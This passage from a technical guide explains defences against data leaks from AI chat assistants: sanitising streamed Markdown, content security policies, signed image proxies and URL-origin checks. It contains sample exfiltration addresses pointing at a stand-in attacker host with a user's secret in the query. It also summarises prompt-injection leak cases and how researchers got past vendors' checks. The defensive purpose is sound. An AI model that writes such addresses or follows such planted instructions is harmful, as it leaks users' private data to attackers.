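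Cleaning each fragment separately doesn't work either. Suppose Dana's image arrives in three pieces, split in the middle of the word "logo" and again in the middle of the host name. No piece is an image on its own, so all three pass, and the browser joins them. Chrome for Developers' *Best practices to render streamed LLM responses* (2025) therefore tells developers to check all the text received so far, and to stop displaying the response if the sanitiser removes anything.

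However, the sample code in that guide runs DOMPurify on the combined text before passing it to a Markdown parser. DOMPurify looks for HTML, and Dana's line of Markdown contains none, so the line would pass the check and then become an image. Newer advice for Chrome developers (Nalpas, 2026) parses first and cleans second, which is the right order, but its sample code permits images with addresses, so the picture would still load. Removing images from the list of permitted tags might not be enough, because the sample builds the answer in the user's browser before cleaning it. A developer who copies either guide still needs a separate rule for images.

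The safest approach is to hold back text until its meaning is clear. An asterisk, for example, might begin a list item, italic text or bold text, and the parser can't tell which until more characters arrive. Shopify handles this in its Sidekick assistant with a program that reads the stream one character at a time. It passes ordinary text straight through, stores anything that looks like the start of a Markdown element, and renders the element once it is complete. A simpler version holds back whole blocks, such as a paragraph up to the blank line that ends it:

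```
for each fragment from the model:
    add the fragment to the buffer
    while the buffer begins with a complete block:
        take the block out of the buffer
        send clean(parse(block)) to the display
when the model stops:
    send clean(parse(buffer)) to the display
```

Suppose the model gives Dana this answer:

```
The tender closes on **Friday**.

![logo](https://img.attacker.example/logo.png?v=482000)

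<img src="https://img.attacker.example/b.png?v=482000">

See [the tender](https://img.attacker.example/t?v=482000).
```

The first paragraph is complete at the blank line, so the server sends it on with its bold text. The image arrives in three pieces, which the server keeps in the buffer until the next blank line. The parser then finds a single image node with a remote address, and the cleaning function replaces it with a placeholder. The third block is raw HTML, so the function escapes it. The last one contains a link, which loses its destination but keeps its text. The display receives:

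```
<p>The tender closes on <strong>Friday</strong>.</p>
<p>[Image removed: logo]</p>
&lt;img src=&quot;https://img.attacker.example/b.png?v=482000&quot;&gt;
<p>See the tender (https://img.attacker.example/t?v=482000).</p>
```

The browser makes no request. Dana can see a strange address with her price in it, which may alert her that something is wrong. If the application sends answers by email or Slack, it should leave out the address to avoid automatic links and previews.

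Holding blocks back also deals with Markdown in which later text changes the meaning of earlier text. A reference-style image becomes an image only when its address arrives, which may be at the end of the answer. By then the server has already sent the first part as ordinary text, and it stays that way. Legitimate reference-style links also fail, so users sometimes see stray brackets. TanStack, which publishes open-source tools for web developers, warns of a similar problem with front matter, a block of settings at the top of a Markdown file. A closing line that arrives late can turn the beginning of an answer into settings, so TanStack recommends turning off front matter for AI output.

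### Libraries and products that block remote images

Developers rarely write all this themselves, so their libraries' default settings matter a good deal. Vercel's *harden-react-markdown*, an add-on for a popular Markdown renderer, blocks every image and link until the developer lists the permitted ones. It can replace a blocked image with a notice containing its label, show the label alone, or remove the image. It also blocks embedded images unless the developer enables them.

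Streamdown, another renderer from Vercel, has the opposite defaults and lets through all images and links. Its documentation describes the defaults as permissive, to allow as much functionality as possible, and recommends a stricter configuration for AI-generated text. If developers supply their own list of processing steps, it replaces the default list entirely, so leaving out the sanitiser removes its protection against scripts. TanStack's renderer falls between the two. It escapes raw HTML by default, including during streaming, but leaves the application to handle remote images and links.

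Gemini is the clearest example of a consumer product that follows the strict rule. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) states that Gemini's Markdown sanitiser identifies external image addresses and does not render them, so the image leak in EchoLeak does not apply to Gemini. Researchers at Tenable provide some outside confirmation, having noticed that Gemini no longer displayed remote Markdown images or handled links as it once had. Google combines the sanitiser with classifiers meant to detect planted instructions, reminders to the model to stick to the user's task, and confirmation before risky actions.

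Google does not apply the rule to all its products. In June 2026, 0DIN, a program that pays researchers for flaws in AI products, described a leak through Antigravity, Google's coding tool, which still displayed remote images in its chat. The planted instructions called for the same image in five formats, in case the renderer blocked some of them.

GitHub adopted the rule after trying a more permissive one. It had limited which servers could supply images to Copilot Chat, but Legit Security's *CamoLeak* showed that data could leak through approved addresses. GitHub then disabled image rendering in Copilot Chat completely, and reported the flaw fixed as of 14 August 2025. It could have tried to repair the existing system, so its decision is some evidence that a coding assistant can do without images in its answers.

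### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI offers a much broader set of restrictions as an option called Lockdown Mode. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced it for organisations in February, and personal accounts followed in June. With Lockdown Mode on, ChatGPT may not show images in ordinary answers or retrieve them from the web. It can browse only cached copies of pages that OpenAI already holds, so no live request leaves the company's network. An attacker who runs the website therefore learns nothing from the visit, though the user may get an outdated page.

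According to OpenAI's current help page, *Lockdown Mode*, the mode also turns off deep research, which produces long reports from many sources, and agent mode, in which ChatGPT carries out tasks on websites. ChatGPT can't download files for analysis, and users can't give network access to code written in Canvas, its editing window. They can still upload their own files and generate images. They can also turn the mode off for a single chat, which is convenient but makes the protection depend partly on their choosing the right chat.

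OpenAI says that Lockdown Mode "is not intended for everyone" and is for people and organisations that handle sensitive data. In the February announcement, it described a smaller group, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations, and said most users did not need the mode. Limiting the audience is reasonable for a setting that removes live browsing and agents, but the same reasoning applies much less to blocking remote images alone, which Google does for every Gemini user.

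Lockdown Mode doesn't change network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. In company-managed workspaces, it doesn't automatically disable every connected app, so administrators have to choose which apps and actions to allow. OpenAI advises them not to let an app write anything unless they can confirm that an attacker won't see the result. Even in Lockdown Mode, data may still leak through those apps, an unforeseen combination of features, or a new technique.

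### What users lose, and what can replace it

Without remote images, an answer can't include a chart from a news article, a photograph of a hotel or a picture from a source it cites. This makes a shopping assistant much less useful, since people want to see what they are buying. OpenAI disables its shopping features in Lockdown Mode.

Some pictures are easy to replace. If the user wants a chart, the application can draw one from the numbers in the answer and store it on its own server. It can store generated images there too. Users can also supply pictures. GitHub's *Copilot vision is generally available* (2026) says that people can attach images and PDFs to Copilot Chat on github.com, so disabling pictures in the answers did not prevent developers from asking about a screenshot. An uploaded picture requires no request to a third-party server, although Microsoft points out that images can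 contain planted instructions too.

Product photographs and pictures from the web are harder to show without loading anything remote. An application could copy them into its own storage, as a shop does with its catalogue, and let the model choose among them by ID. The copying has to happen before the conversation. If the server instead fetches a picture during the conversation from an address the model wrote, the server sends Dana's price to the attacker, just as her browser would have.

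### Links and tools that fetch pages

Making links unclickable prevents one-click leaks, but it is a serious drawback for a search assistant, whose users want to open the sources. Google keeps working links in Gemini and checks them with Safe Browsing, its service for identifying dangerous sites. If Gemini summarises a document containing a link that the service considers unsafe, the user sees "suspicious link removed" instead. This works for known phishing sites, but an attacker can register a new domain with no bad record and use it only to collect data. Checkmarx, a software security company, credits Gemini's sanitiser with preventing zero-click image leaks like EchoLeak, but links that the user clicks need a different defense.

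Blocking images also doesn't stop an assistant's own tools from leaking data. Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* describes how planted instructions could make Gemini open a page whose address contained the user's saved information and location. Gemini's image protections didn't apply, because the browsing tool made the request and nothing had to appear on the screen. The tool did not adequately check the destination or ask the user first. Google has since fixed the flaw.

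Anthropic restricts Claude's page-fetching tool to exact addresses that the user typed or that its search tool returned. This stops the model from adding private data to an address it makes up, but Willison reports that Ayush Paul found a hole in the design. Even a tool that takes no address can leak a little. Microsoft notes that if an attacker can see whether the assistant used a tool, planted instructions can leak one bit of information by making the assistant use it or not.

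## Loading only from approved sites

An allowlist restores most of the pictures that the strict rule removes. The developer lists the servers that images may load from, and the viewer blocks every other address. A shopping assistant can then display photographs from the shop's image server, including ones added that morning. A picture like Dana's fails to load because img.attacker.example is not on the list.

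The browser can enforce the list through a content security policy (CSP), which it checks just before making a request. A sanitiser has to recognise every element that could cause a request, in whatever notation the model used, whereas the browser applies the same rule to a reference-style image, a CSS background or a picture in a Mermaid diagram. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) offers some evidence that this helps. The attack it describes had already got past Microsoft's injection detector and link filter when the CSP blocked the image, and the data got out only once the researchers had found an approved Microsoft service to relay the request.

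An administrator can also review the list of approved sites and ask why each one is there, which is manageable for twenty host names. Nobody can inspect a model's tendency to refuse planted instructions in the same way. Salesforce, which sells software for managing customers, stores each approved site as a separate configuration file, according to its documentation page *CspTrustedSite*. A company that keeps those files in version control can see who added a site and when.

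### A content security policy, line by line

A web server sends the policy along with the page. An assistant that displays a shop's photographs might use this one, split across lines here for easier reading:

```
Content-Security-Policy:
    default-src 'none';
    script-src 'self';
    style-src 'self';
    img-src 'self' https://images.shop.example;
    connect-src 'self';
    font-src 'self';
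    frame-src https://preview.example;
    form-action 'self'
```

Each line is a directive. Its first word names a kind of request, and the rest lists the permitted destinations. The word 'self' means the site that the page came from, and 'none' means nowhere. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the standard, defines them as follows:

- `default-src` applies to any kind of resource without a directive of its own. Here that includes video and sound, which the page can't load at all.
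- `script-src` and `style-src` let the application load its own code and style sheets. As written, they also make the browser ignore any scripts and style attributes in HTML that the model wrote.
- `img-src` covers pictures, including CSS backgrounds.
- `connect-src` covers requests that scripts make. It also covers an attribute called "ping", which makes a link notify a second address when someone clicks it.
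- `font-src` covers font files.
- `frame-src` covers other web pages displayed inside this one.
- `form-action` limits where a form can send its contents.

When Dana's browser reaches the image tag, it looks for img.attacker.example in the `img-src` line, doesn't find it, and drops the request before contacting the server.

W3C warns that a policy without `default-src` cannot prevent exfiltration, because some requests, such as prefetches, have no directive of their own and the browser always allows them when `default-src` is missing. If the policy includes `default-src`, the browser prefetches only from servers that appear somewhere in the policy. One loose directive can undo the others. W3C's example is a policy that forbids everything by default but allows images from any server, which would let Dana's price leak. According to CentralCSP's *default-src*, `form-action` never falls back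 to the default, so it needs its own line.

Developers can test a policy before enforcing it by sending it under a different header name, which makes the browser report violations without blocking anything. Reports remain useful after launch because an attempt to contact an unknown server may mean that someone has planted instructions. However, a report includes the blocked address, which would contain Dana's price. W3C also advises developers to treat reports as text that an attacker may have written, and to escape them before displaying them. Otherwise, a dashboard that shows the reports could leak data as OpenAI's log viewer did.

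A CSP controls which servers the browser contacts but has little control over the rest of the address. A directive can include a path, such as `https://images.shop.example/products/`, but the browser ignores the query when it compares addresses, so it would allow a product photograph with "?v=482000" on the end. That does no harm as long as the attacker can't read the shop's logs or make the shop's server pass the request on. If the shop's server redirects the browser to another host, the browser checks that host against the list too, but not the path. W3C chose to skip the path check because a site could otherwise use its own policy to discover where a redirect had taken the user.

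### Clicked links and other gaps

No directive controls where a clicked link can go. If Dana clicks a link to the attacker's server, her browser opens it regardless of the policy. This was deliberate. According to an early Mozilla design note, the policy was meant to restrict what a page uses, not to stop "navigation to arbitrary sites".

A directive called `navigate-to`, later proposed for the standard, would have limited where a page could send its user. CentralCSP's *navigate-to* reports that its handling of redirects and moves between sites was never settled, and that it was removed in September 2022. Mozilla's *Remove navigate-to CSP directive* records that no browser had shipped it. A product that relies on a CSP therefore needs a separate rule for links, such as making them unclickable.

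The policy above would not stop a redirect tag from sending Dana's browser tab to the attacker's site, because `form-action` applies only to forms. A tag that only makes the browser look up a host name may also get through, since there may be no request for the browser to check. The sanitiser has to remove both kinds of tag. W3C recommends a CSP as an extra layer of defence alongside careful cleaning of the output.

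A CSP does not affect link previews or requests that a server makes, such as an assistant's web searches or an image proxy's fetches.

### What an image proxy hides and what it passes on

Some products display pictures from far too many sites to list. They often use an image proxy, which works like this:

1. The application finds the address of an outside picture and replaces it with an address on the proxy. The new address contains the old one.
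2. The user's browser requests the picture from the proxy.
3. The proxy extracts the original address and requests the picture from that server.
4. The proxy sends the picture back to the browser.

GitHub built a proxy called Camo to avoid browser warnings about images from unencrypted sites. GitHub's *Proxying User Images* (2014) announced that images from encrypted sites would go through it too, to keep information about users' browsers from third parties. GitLab's *Proxying assets* describes the main worry, which is that someone can post a comment containing an image hosted on their own server and log the IP address of everyone who reads it.

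These are good reasons to use a proxy, but they concern the reader's privacy and not the contents of Dana's mailbox. Suppose that her chat window uses a proxy that fetches any address. The image tag becomes:

```
<img src="https://proxy.example/?url=https%3A%2F%2Fimg.attacker.example%2Flogo.png%3Fv%3D482000">
```

The proxy decodes the address and asks the attacker's server for "/logo.png?v=482000", exactly as Dana's browser would have done.

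| What the attacker's server receives | Browser loads the picture | Proxy loads the picture |
|---|---|---|
| The user's network address | Yes | No, only the proxy's |
| Cookies from earlier visits | Sometimes | No |
| The page the user was reading | Sometimes | No |
| The type of browser | Yes | No |
| The picture's full address, with the price | Yes | Yes |

Caching by a proxy does not prevent the leak. Proxies usually keep copies of pictures so they don't have to contact the original server every time, but an address containing a new secret is one the proxy has never fetched before, so it has to contact the server.

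An unrestricted proxy also makes the CSP useless against this leak. Every picture comes from proxy.example, which the developer has to list under `img-src`, so the browser allows all of them. Either the proxy has to check the real destination, or the application has to check it before creating the proxy address.

GitLab's `asset_proxy_allowlist` setting lists the sites whose images skip the proxy and load directly. The proxy fetches images from all other sites. The setting's name could easily mislead someone into thinking that images can come only from the listed sites.

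### Making a proxy refuse

The simplest restriction is a list of domains at the proxy. Cloudflare lets customers of its image service restrict images to certain domains and, optionally, to paths with a certain beginning. Go-Camo, a newer version of Camo that GitLab recommends, accepts lists of permitted and forbidden sites. According to its documentation, the application should preferably do the filtering when it creates the proxy address, with the proxy's own lists as a fallback.

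The proxy has to repeat the check whenever a server redirects it. Cloudflare checks only the first address and then follows redirects, even to domains that the customer never listed. Some websites have a page that forwards visitors to any address named in the query. If an approved site has such a page, planted instructions could use it to send the price through the proxy to the attacker. Under a CSP, by contrast, the browser checks the host after every redirect.

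Limiting the number of redirects is a weaker measure because an attacker needs only one. By default, Camo follows up to four, Go-Camo three, and imgproxy, another open-source proxy, ten. Setting the limit to zero solves the problem, but images that have moved won't load.

A proxy should also refuse addresses on its operator's internal network, because an attacker could try to use it to reach machines that outsiders can't, such as an administrator's control panel. Go-Camo rejects private network addresses, whether they appear in the URL or come from looking up a host name. It can miss internal machines that use public addresses, so its documentation recommends running it on an isolated machine. The documentation also warns that some of these protections may fail if Go-Camo sends its requests through a second proxy, which might follow redirects itself. These measures protect the operator, but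 Dana's price would still leak because the attacker's server is on the public internet.

Stripping the query from every address doesn't stop data from leaking through the path or host name, and it breaks images whose servers use the query to set the size or grant temporary access.

A proxy could combine most of these checks with a signature, which is a code showing that the application approved the address:

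```
function fetch_image(address, signature):
    if signature does not match address:
        refuse
    repeat up to 4 times:
        if the host is not on the list:
            refuse
        ip = look up the host
        if ip belongs to an internal network:
            refuse
        response = request the address from that ip
        if response is a redirect:
            address = the new address
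        else if response is an image of acceptable size:
            return the image
        else:
            refuse
    refuse
```

The proxy checks the host name against the approved list before looking up its network address, because the lookup itself can leak data. It then checks the address and connects to it without a second lookup, since an attacker who controls the host name could return a different address the second time.

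### How GitHub signs image addresses

Camo's signature is an HMAC, a code that a program computes from a message and a secret key. Without the key, nobody can work out the right code for a message, and changing even one character of the message makes the old code invalid. GitHub's *camo*, the project's documentation, uses the picture's original address as the message. The result is 40 characters long and becomes part of the new address:

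```
https://camo.githubusercontent.com/<signature>/<original address>
```

The original address appears in hexadecimal, so "https://" becomes "68747470733a2f2f". This keeps special characters from being garbled in transit, but anyone can reverse it.

Suppose a project's introductory page includes a chart from `https://pictures.example/chart.png`. When GitHub renders the page, it signs the chart's address and replaces it with the Camo version. A reader's browser then requests the chart from Camo, which GitHub's CSP permits because the server belongs to GitHub. Camo recomputes the signature and, if it matches the one in the request, fetches the chart, checks that it is a permitted type of image and sends it to the browser. By default, Camo rejects files larger than about five megabytes and times out after ten seconds.

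Suppose that planted instructions tell Copilot Chat to leak a password through a picture. The CSP stops the browser from loading an image directly from the attacker's server. The model could write a Camo address for the chart with the password added to the query, but the chart's existing signature wouldn't match the changed address. The model doesn't have the key to compute a new signature, so it can only repeat addresses that GitHub has already signed.

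The protection depends on when the application signs picture addresses. If it signed every address in a finished answer, it would sign Dana's too, and the proxy would fetch the picture. The application should sign only addresses that it obtained before the model began to write, and refuse any others in the answer. Similarly, a developer of imgproxy points out that if browser code can create valid addresses, so can anyone else. imgproxy's *Signing the URL* presents signatures mainly as a way to stop people from overloading the server with requests for resized pictures. imgproxy doesn't check signatures unless the operator turns the feature on, and a developer adding imgproxy to a chat window could easily miss this.

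A valid signature also doesn't mean an address is harmless. Legit Security notes that anyone can submit Markdown to GitHub's API and get back signed addresses, which is how the CamoLeak researchers prepared theirs in advance.

### Web pages that the model writes

Some assistants write entire web pages and small apps, which ChatGPT displays in Canvas and Claude displays as artifacts. These pages usually need scripts, so a sanitiser that removed scripts would break them. A developer can instead run the page in a frame that loads from a separate domain. Browsers prevent a script on one site from reading a page on another, so the generated page can't read the conversation around it.

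GitHub used the same separation for files its users upload. It announced in *New user content domains* (2014) that it would serve these files from githubusercontent.com instead of github.com, in case they contained hostile code.

Isolation does not protect data that is already inside the generated page. If Dana asks for a chart of her firm's tenders, the page contains the price, and a script that the model wrote under an attacker's influence could send it out. The frame therefore needs a policy of its own:

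```
Content-Security-Policy:
    default-src 'none';
    script-src 'unsafe-inline';
    style-src 'unsafe-inline';
    img-src data:;
    form-action 'none';
    webrtc 'block';
    sandbox allow-scripts
```

The two 'unsafe-inline' entries let the page use the scripts and styles written into it. That would be risky in the chat window, but here the scripts can steal little except the page's own contents, and the other lines limit where they can send that data. The separate `webrtc` directive stops scripts from using WebRTC, a system for direct connections such as video calls, in browsers that support it. The last line puts the page in a sandbox where scripts can run but can't open new windows or redirect the surrounding chat page.

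A script could still try to navigate the frame itself to the attacker's address, with the price in the query. The frame's own policy does not govern navigation, but the chat window's `frame-src` directive limits which addresses may load in its frames. In the earlier example, it permits only preview.example. The developer needs both policies to close the leak.

Some applications put the generated code straight into a frame instead of loading it from another site. Under W3C's rules, the frame then inherits the chat window's policy, so that a page cannot escape its policy by opening a frame. The chat policy above forbids scripts written into the page, so a generated app would not run. Loosening the policy would let the app run but remove some of the chat window's protection, a conflict that developers can avoid by loading the app from a separate domain.

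OpenAI runs Canvas apps and third-party ChatGPT apps in a sandbox that can detect unexpected communications and ask the user for consent. This is more flexible than a fixed allowlist because a generated weather app could contact a forecasting service that no administrator had approved in advance. However, the protection then depends partly on the user's answer.

### Salesforce's Trusted URLs

Salesforce uses a single list of approved sites for both the browser's policy and the text its AI agents produce. According to Salesforce's *Content Security Policy Overview*, the default policy lets pages load pictures, fonts, frames and other resources only from the customer's own Salesforce site. Administrators can approve outside sites, which Salesforce calls Trusted URLs. According to *Manage Trusted URLs*, they choose what each site may supply, such as images but not frames, and which kinds of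 Salesforce page the approval covers. Only people with two powerful administrative permissions can change the list.

TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* reports that Salesforce began applying the list to its AI products on 8 September 2025. Salesforce Ben, a news site for Salesforce users, notes that the security company Noma had reported a leak through a generated image in July.

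PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* describes how Agentforce, Salesforce's system of AI agents, replaces every address that isn't on the approved list with "[URL_REDACTED]" before displaying an answer in its chat window. It does this for both links and images, in Markdown, HTML and CSS. This deals with the largest gap in a CSP, because it leaves users no unapproved link to click. But administrators have to list every outside site their agents need to cite, and users lose links to any site the administrators forget.

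When an administrator adds a site in Salesforce, the box that approves images from it is ticked by default. An administrator who only wants links to a supplier's website to work will therefore accidentally approve its images too, unless they clear the box. PromptArmor advises administrators to clear it for any site that doesn't need to supply images, and warns against wildcard entries, such as "*.example.com", for services where anyone can publish content.

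Salesforce adds its own addresses to each directive, changes them regularly and doesn't show them among the Trusted URLs. An administrator who wants to see every address the browser may contact has to inspect the policy that the browser receives. Long lists can also cause problems because some network equipment rejects large headers. Salesforce recommends keeping each policy on its public-facing sites under three kilobytes, which is enough for roughly a hundred entries of thirty characters.

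Trusted URLs do not control requests from code that runs on Salesforce's servers. Administrators keep a separate list for those requests. PromptArmor recommends having a person approve the actions an agent takes with its tools, to prevent attacks like the one on Copilot Cowork.

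## Approving the exact address by its origin

An allowlist of sites approves any address on a trusted supplier's website, even one with Dana's price added to the end. Another approach is to check whether the exact address could contain the user's secrets, regardless of the site's reputation.

Whether an address can leak data usually depends on where it came from. Suppose Dana's firm had priced its tender at 497,000 instead of 482,000. The address of a supplier's catalogue would be the same, because the supplier chose it without knowing the price, but the address that the model wrote for the attacker would end in "497000". If a program can establish that someone chose an address without knowledge of Dana's mail, the text of that address can't reveal her price, whoever runs the server.

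*Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026) explains why the alternatives work badly for agents. Current frameworks ask for permission once per tool, so a user who approves web search also approves every address the tool later requests. The user usually sees those addresses only in shortened form. Site allowlists are impractical for an assistant that must consult many sources. Scanning addresses for suspiciously encoded text produces many false alarms because ordinary websites routinely encode values in their addresses.

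OpenAI, Google and Anthropic have each built a check on the exact address, but they accept different evidence that its origin is harmless.

### OpenAI's public index

OpenAI considered a list of well-known sites and decided it would help but not be enough. One reason was that many legitimate sites have pages that forward visitors to other sites. Tenable (2025) found that OpenAI's earlier check always approved addresses on bing.com, and used this to get past the check to any website. OpenAI also worried that a strict list would show people warnings too often, because they visit far more than a handful of popular sites, and that they would learn to click through without thinking.

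An exact check handles forwarding pages better. Suppose the model writes this address:

```
https://trusted.example/go?to=https://img.attacker.example/t?v=482000
```

A site list that checks only the first host approves a forwarding address with Dana's price in it. An exact check refuses it because nobody has published that address. The model could still use a published forwarding address, but only unchanged. That address might take the visitor to an unexpected site, but it would not send the price there.

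OpenAI's check works as follows:

1. A crawler scans public web pages, as a search engine does, and records the addresses it finds. It has no access to conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. When ChatGPT is about to load an address automatically, OpenAI's software looks for that address in the crawler's records.
3. If it finds a match, ChatGPT loads the page or picture.
4. If it finds none, the software either tells the agent to try a different site or warns the user before opening the address.

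This works only if the crawler is independent of the conversations. If OpenAI added the addresses that ChatGPT wrote to the crawler's index, Dana's leaked address would count as known the second time the model used it.

OpenAI calls the system Safe Url. It covers ordinary chats, the pages the agent opens and the bookmarks it creates in OpenAI's Atlas browser, and the searches and page visits in deep research. Bookmarks need the check because opening a saved address later sends any data it contains.

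In 2023, Rehberger guessed that ChatGPT might be looking images up in Bing's index. Embrace The Red reports that OpenAI built its own index instead, and dates the stronger protection to about August 2025, some months before OpenAI published a technical paper on it. As Rehberger understands it, ChatGPT also accepts any address the user types, for the rest of that chat. He considers the system a significant improvement but doubts that every developer at OpenAI will know to use it. His doubt has some basis, since the phone and Mac apps lacked the first version of the check.

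The index will always lack some harmless addresses. It may not yet include a news article published ten minutes ago, and it should not include the unlisted link to a document that a colleague shared with Dana, or a page of search results for an unusual phrase. When an address is missing, ChatGPT has to find another source or interrupt her. This is probably less of a nuisance than a list of approved sites would be, because the crawler can record millions of pages on sites that no administrator would have thought to approve.

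OpenAI promises only that the agent will not quietly leak the user's data through the URL itself. An approved page may still contain lies or planted instructions, and the promise doesn't cover text that the agent types into a form.

### Google's record of where an address came from

Google records where each address came from and allows only those it can trace to a source that cannot compose text, such as a search result or the user's message. It doesn't need to know whether an address is public. This rule excludes the model as a source because it can combine an attacker's host name with something from Dana's mailbox. A website's owner chose the address in a search result, and the search engine only passes it on.

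The record of origins blocks Dana's address because that address didn't appear in any search result or in any of her messages. Unlike Safe Browsing, Gemini's other check on links, it works even if the attacker's domain doesn't have a bad reputation.

The software first has to recognise an address in every format that the viewer will turn into a link, from Markdown's reference style to bare text. It also has to decide when two spellings count as the same address. When copying a link, a model may drop the "https://" or capitalise a letter in the host name, and a user would be puzzled to see the link blocked.

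When comparing addresses, the software can safely ignore capitalization in the host name, which doesn't change its meaning, and the fragment, which the browser doesn't send. Ignoring some other small differences would let the model encode data in the address. For example, if the software ignored the order of the values in a query, the model could arrange five different values in 120 ways, and the attacker's server would receive the order it used.

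One way to avoid this is to use the model's version only to look up the original, and then put the recorded original into the link:

```
function safe_link(address, recorded):
    for each original in recorded:
        if simplify(original) equals simplify(address):
            return original
    return nothing
```

Here "simplify" removes whatever differences the developer has decided to tolerate. However the model varied the spelling, the browser would request the same text.

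Typing errors are harder to handle, because sometimes the recorded address is the wrong one. If Dana types "suplier.example" and the model corrects it to "supplier.example", she wants the corrected link, which appears nowhere in her message. Google's system has to allow such corrections without letting the model alter addresses freely. If the rule let the model change any one character, and an attacker had got an address with a 40-character path into the search results, the model could produce 1,401 versions of it, including the original, using only lowercase letters and digits. Two such addresses would give nearly two million combinations, enough to encode any six-digit price.

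A safer rule would accept a corrected address only if it matched one the software had already received from another source, such as a search result. The software could also show the correction to the user for approval.

Google's rule has small exceptions too, and a developer copying the design should check how many different addresses the model could produce under each one. An exception for home pages, for instance, would permit "482000.attacker.example", which has no path or query but contains the price in its host name.

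Gavish (2026), in *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, lists URL sanitization among Google's deterministic defenses, along with user confirmation and rules on which tools an agent may use in sequence. A central policy engine controls all of them, so Google can respond to a new attack by changing a setting, for example to block a particular text pattern, without waiting to retrain a model. Such a fix stops a known attack, but the origin rule also applies to attacker addresses that Google has never seen.

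Google also needs to apply the check wherever Gemini can make a request. A check on the links in the finished answer would have come too late to stop the leak through Gemini's browsing tool that Tenable reported.

### Anthropic's web fetch tool

Anthropic applies a similar rule to a tool that fetches pages for Claude, its AI model. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, the documentation for developers as it stood in June 2026, gives the reason for the rule as the risk of exfiltration when Claude handles untrusted text and sensitive data together. Claude may not construct addresses. The tool will fetch an address only if it has already appeared in one of these places:

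- a message from the user;
- the result of a tool that the developer's own software runs;
- a result from Anthropic's web search tool or an earlier fetch.

The tool rejects addresses that come from Anthropic's code execution tools, which run programs on the company's servers. Claude can write a program that joins an attacker's host name to Dana's price and prints the result. The address would then appear in the conversation even though the model composed it.

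In *The Memory Heist*, Paul (2026) tested the rule in Claude's consumer app. Claude opened the home page of his server when he gave it the address. He then asked it to open a page on the same server with his real name in the path, and the request failed. The tool can request pages but can't send separate messages, so his name could only have been sent in the address.

Paul got data out through links on his own pages, and Anthropic then stopped the tool from following links found in fetched pages. The design had impressed Willison (2026) because it deterministically blocks addresses that the model composes.

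In the simplest form, the program around the model keeps a list:

```
approved = empty list

when the user sends a message:
    add the addresses in it to approved
when the search tool returns its results:
    add the address of each result to approved
when the model asks to open an address:
    if the address is in approved:
        open it
    else:
        refuse
```

The model can't add to the list or override it. A careful developer would add only the address of each search result, not addresses in the extract below it, because the website's owner wrote that text and could put any address in it.

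Users often name a page, such as a software project's README, without giving its address. If the search tool is on, Claude searches for the page and then fetches the address that the search returned. This adds a step, but it means the rule rarely interferes with ordinary research.

The tool also rejects addresses longer than 250 characters. This limits how much data a single request can leak, but it would do little to protect Dana, whose price is only six characters long. The limit also blocks some legitimate links, since temporary download links often exceed it.

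Anthropic warns that some risk remains. It suggests that worried developers turn the tool off, limit the number of fetches (there is no default limit), or restrict the tool to known sites. With the last option, an address needs both an acceptable origin and an acceptable host. A company that wants Claude to read only its suppliers' websites loses nothing by adding the site list, which still blocks other sites if the origin check fails.

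### Three addresses compared

Suppose that Dana asks her assistant for the official rules on public tenders, and that the planted email is still in her mailbox. During the conversation, the assistant might try to use any of these addresses:

```
https://img.attacker.example/t?v=482000
https://council.example/tenders/rules.html
https://encyclopedia.example/Tender
```

The model composed the first address from the attacker's host name and Dana's price. It copied the second from a search result. It wrote the third from memory, since its training data included the encyclopedia, and no search in this conversation has returned that address.

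OpenAI's software checks its index for all three addresses. It can't find the first, because no public page contained it, but it probably finds the other two, which lead to established public pages. Google's software finds a source for the council's address in the search results, but none for the first or third address. Anthropic's tool gives the same results as Google's, although it restricts which pages Claude can read, while Google's rule restricts which links Gemini can show.

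| Address | OpenAI | Google | Anthropic |
|---|---|---|---|
| Composed, with the price in it | No match, so ChatGPT tries another site or warns the user | Blocked | Refused |
| Copied from a search result | Loads if the crawler has seen it | Allowed | Fetched |
| Public, but written from memory | Loads if the crawler has seen it | Blocked, unless an exception applies | Refused until a search returns it |

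All three designs stop Dana's leak. None of them relies on recognising "482000" as a price, so encoding the number would not help the attacker.

The two designs differ in which harmless addresses they approve. An index can approve an address that the model produces from its training data, but not one that appeared on the web after the crawler's last visit. A record of the conversation can approve a page published this morning as soon as a search finds it, and it can also approve a private link that Dana pastes in. It is far more practical for a small developer because it doesn't need a crawler. Software could also accept an address if either check approves it, but an attacker would then need to find a weakness in only one of them.

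The designs also give different assurances. OpenAI's establishes that the address existed on the public web independently of Dana's conversation, and Google's that it came from a source that couldn't have written her secrets into it. Anthropic's establishes only that the address appeared in an accepted part of the conversation, which protects her as long as nothing in that part could have composed the address. With all of these designs, the model can still reveal a little by choosing which approved address to open, as Paul's attack showed.

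### Private links in a public index

OpenAI assumes that a public address is unlikely to contain private data. Many addresses contain a token, a long random code that works like a key. Anyone with the full address can reset a password, open a shared document or see a booking. Some of these links become public by accident.

Antipov (2026), in *Защищали от фишинга, а создали новый риск утечки*, a Russian news report, describes LeakyLinks, a study of private links exposed by phishing scanners. Companies often send the links in their employees' email to an outside service that checks them for phishing. Some of these services then publish the scanned addresses because security researchers find them useful. The researchers behind LeakyLinks collected more than two million addresses from the public feeds of six services and found over 4,000 that gave access to sensitive information, including visa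 documents and bookings. They sorted the addresses using a language model on their own servers, with a reported accuracy of 97%.

That is about one address in 500, which is many exposed documents but a small share of the feeds. The figure can't be applied directly to OpenAI's index, because scanners receive links from private email, whereas OpenAI's crawler scans public pages. But if the crawler visited a page that listed scanned addresses, it could pick up the tokens too.

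In Dana's case, a few private links in the index would do little harm, because the attacker needs an indexed address that contains her price and leads to the attacker's own server. A stray link to somebody's visa application leads to the visa service, and its secret is already public. The researchers published decoy pages through the scanners and recorded automated visits to them. They couldn't tell the purpose of the visits, but the visits show that other programs read these feeds.

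The larger danger is that opening some addresses triggers an action. If an index contained a working link that confirmed a password change or logged someone in, an attacker could plant instructions for an agent to open it, and the link would pass the check. OpenAI could reduce this risk by leaving out addresses that seem to contain tokens, though this would cause more warnings on harmless pages.

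### Attacker's text in the user's message

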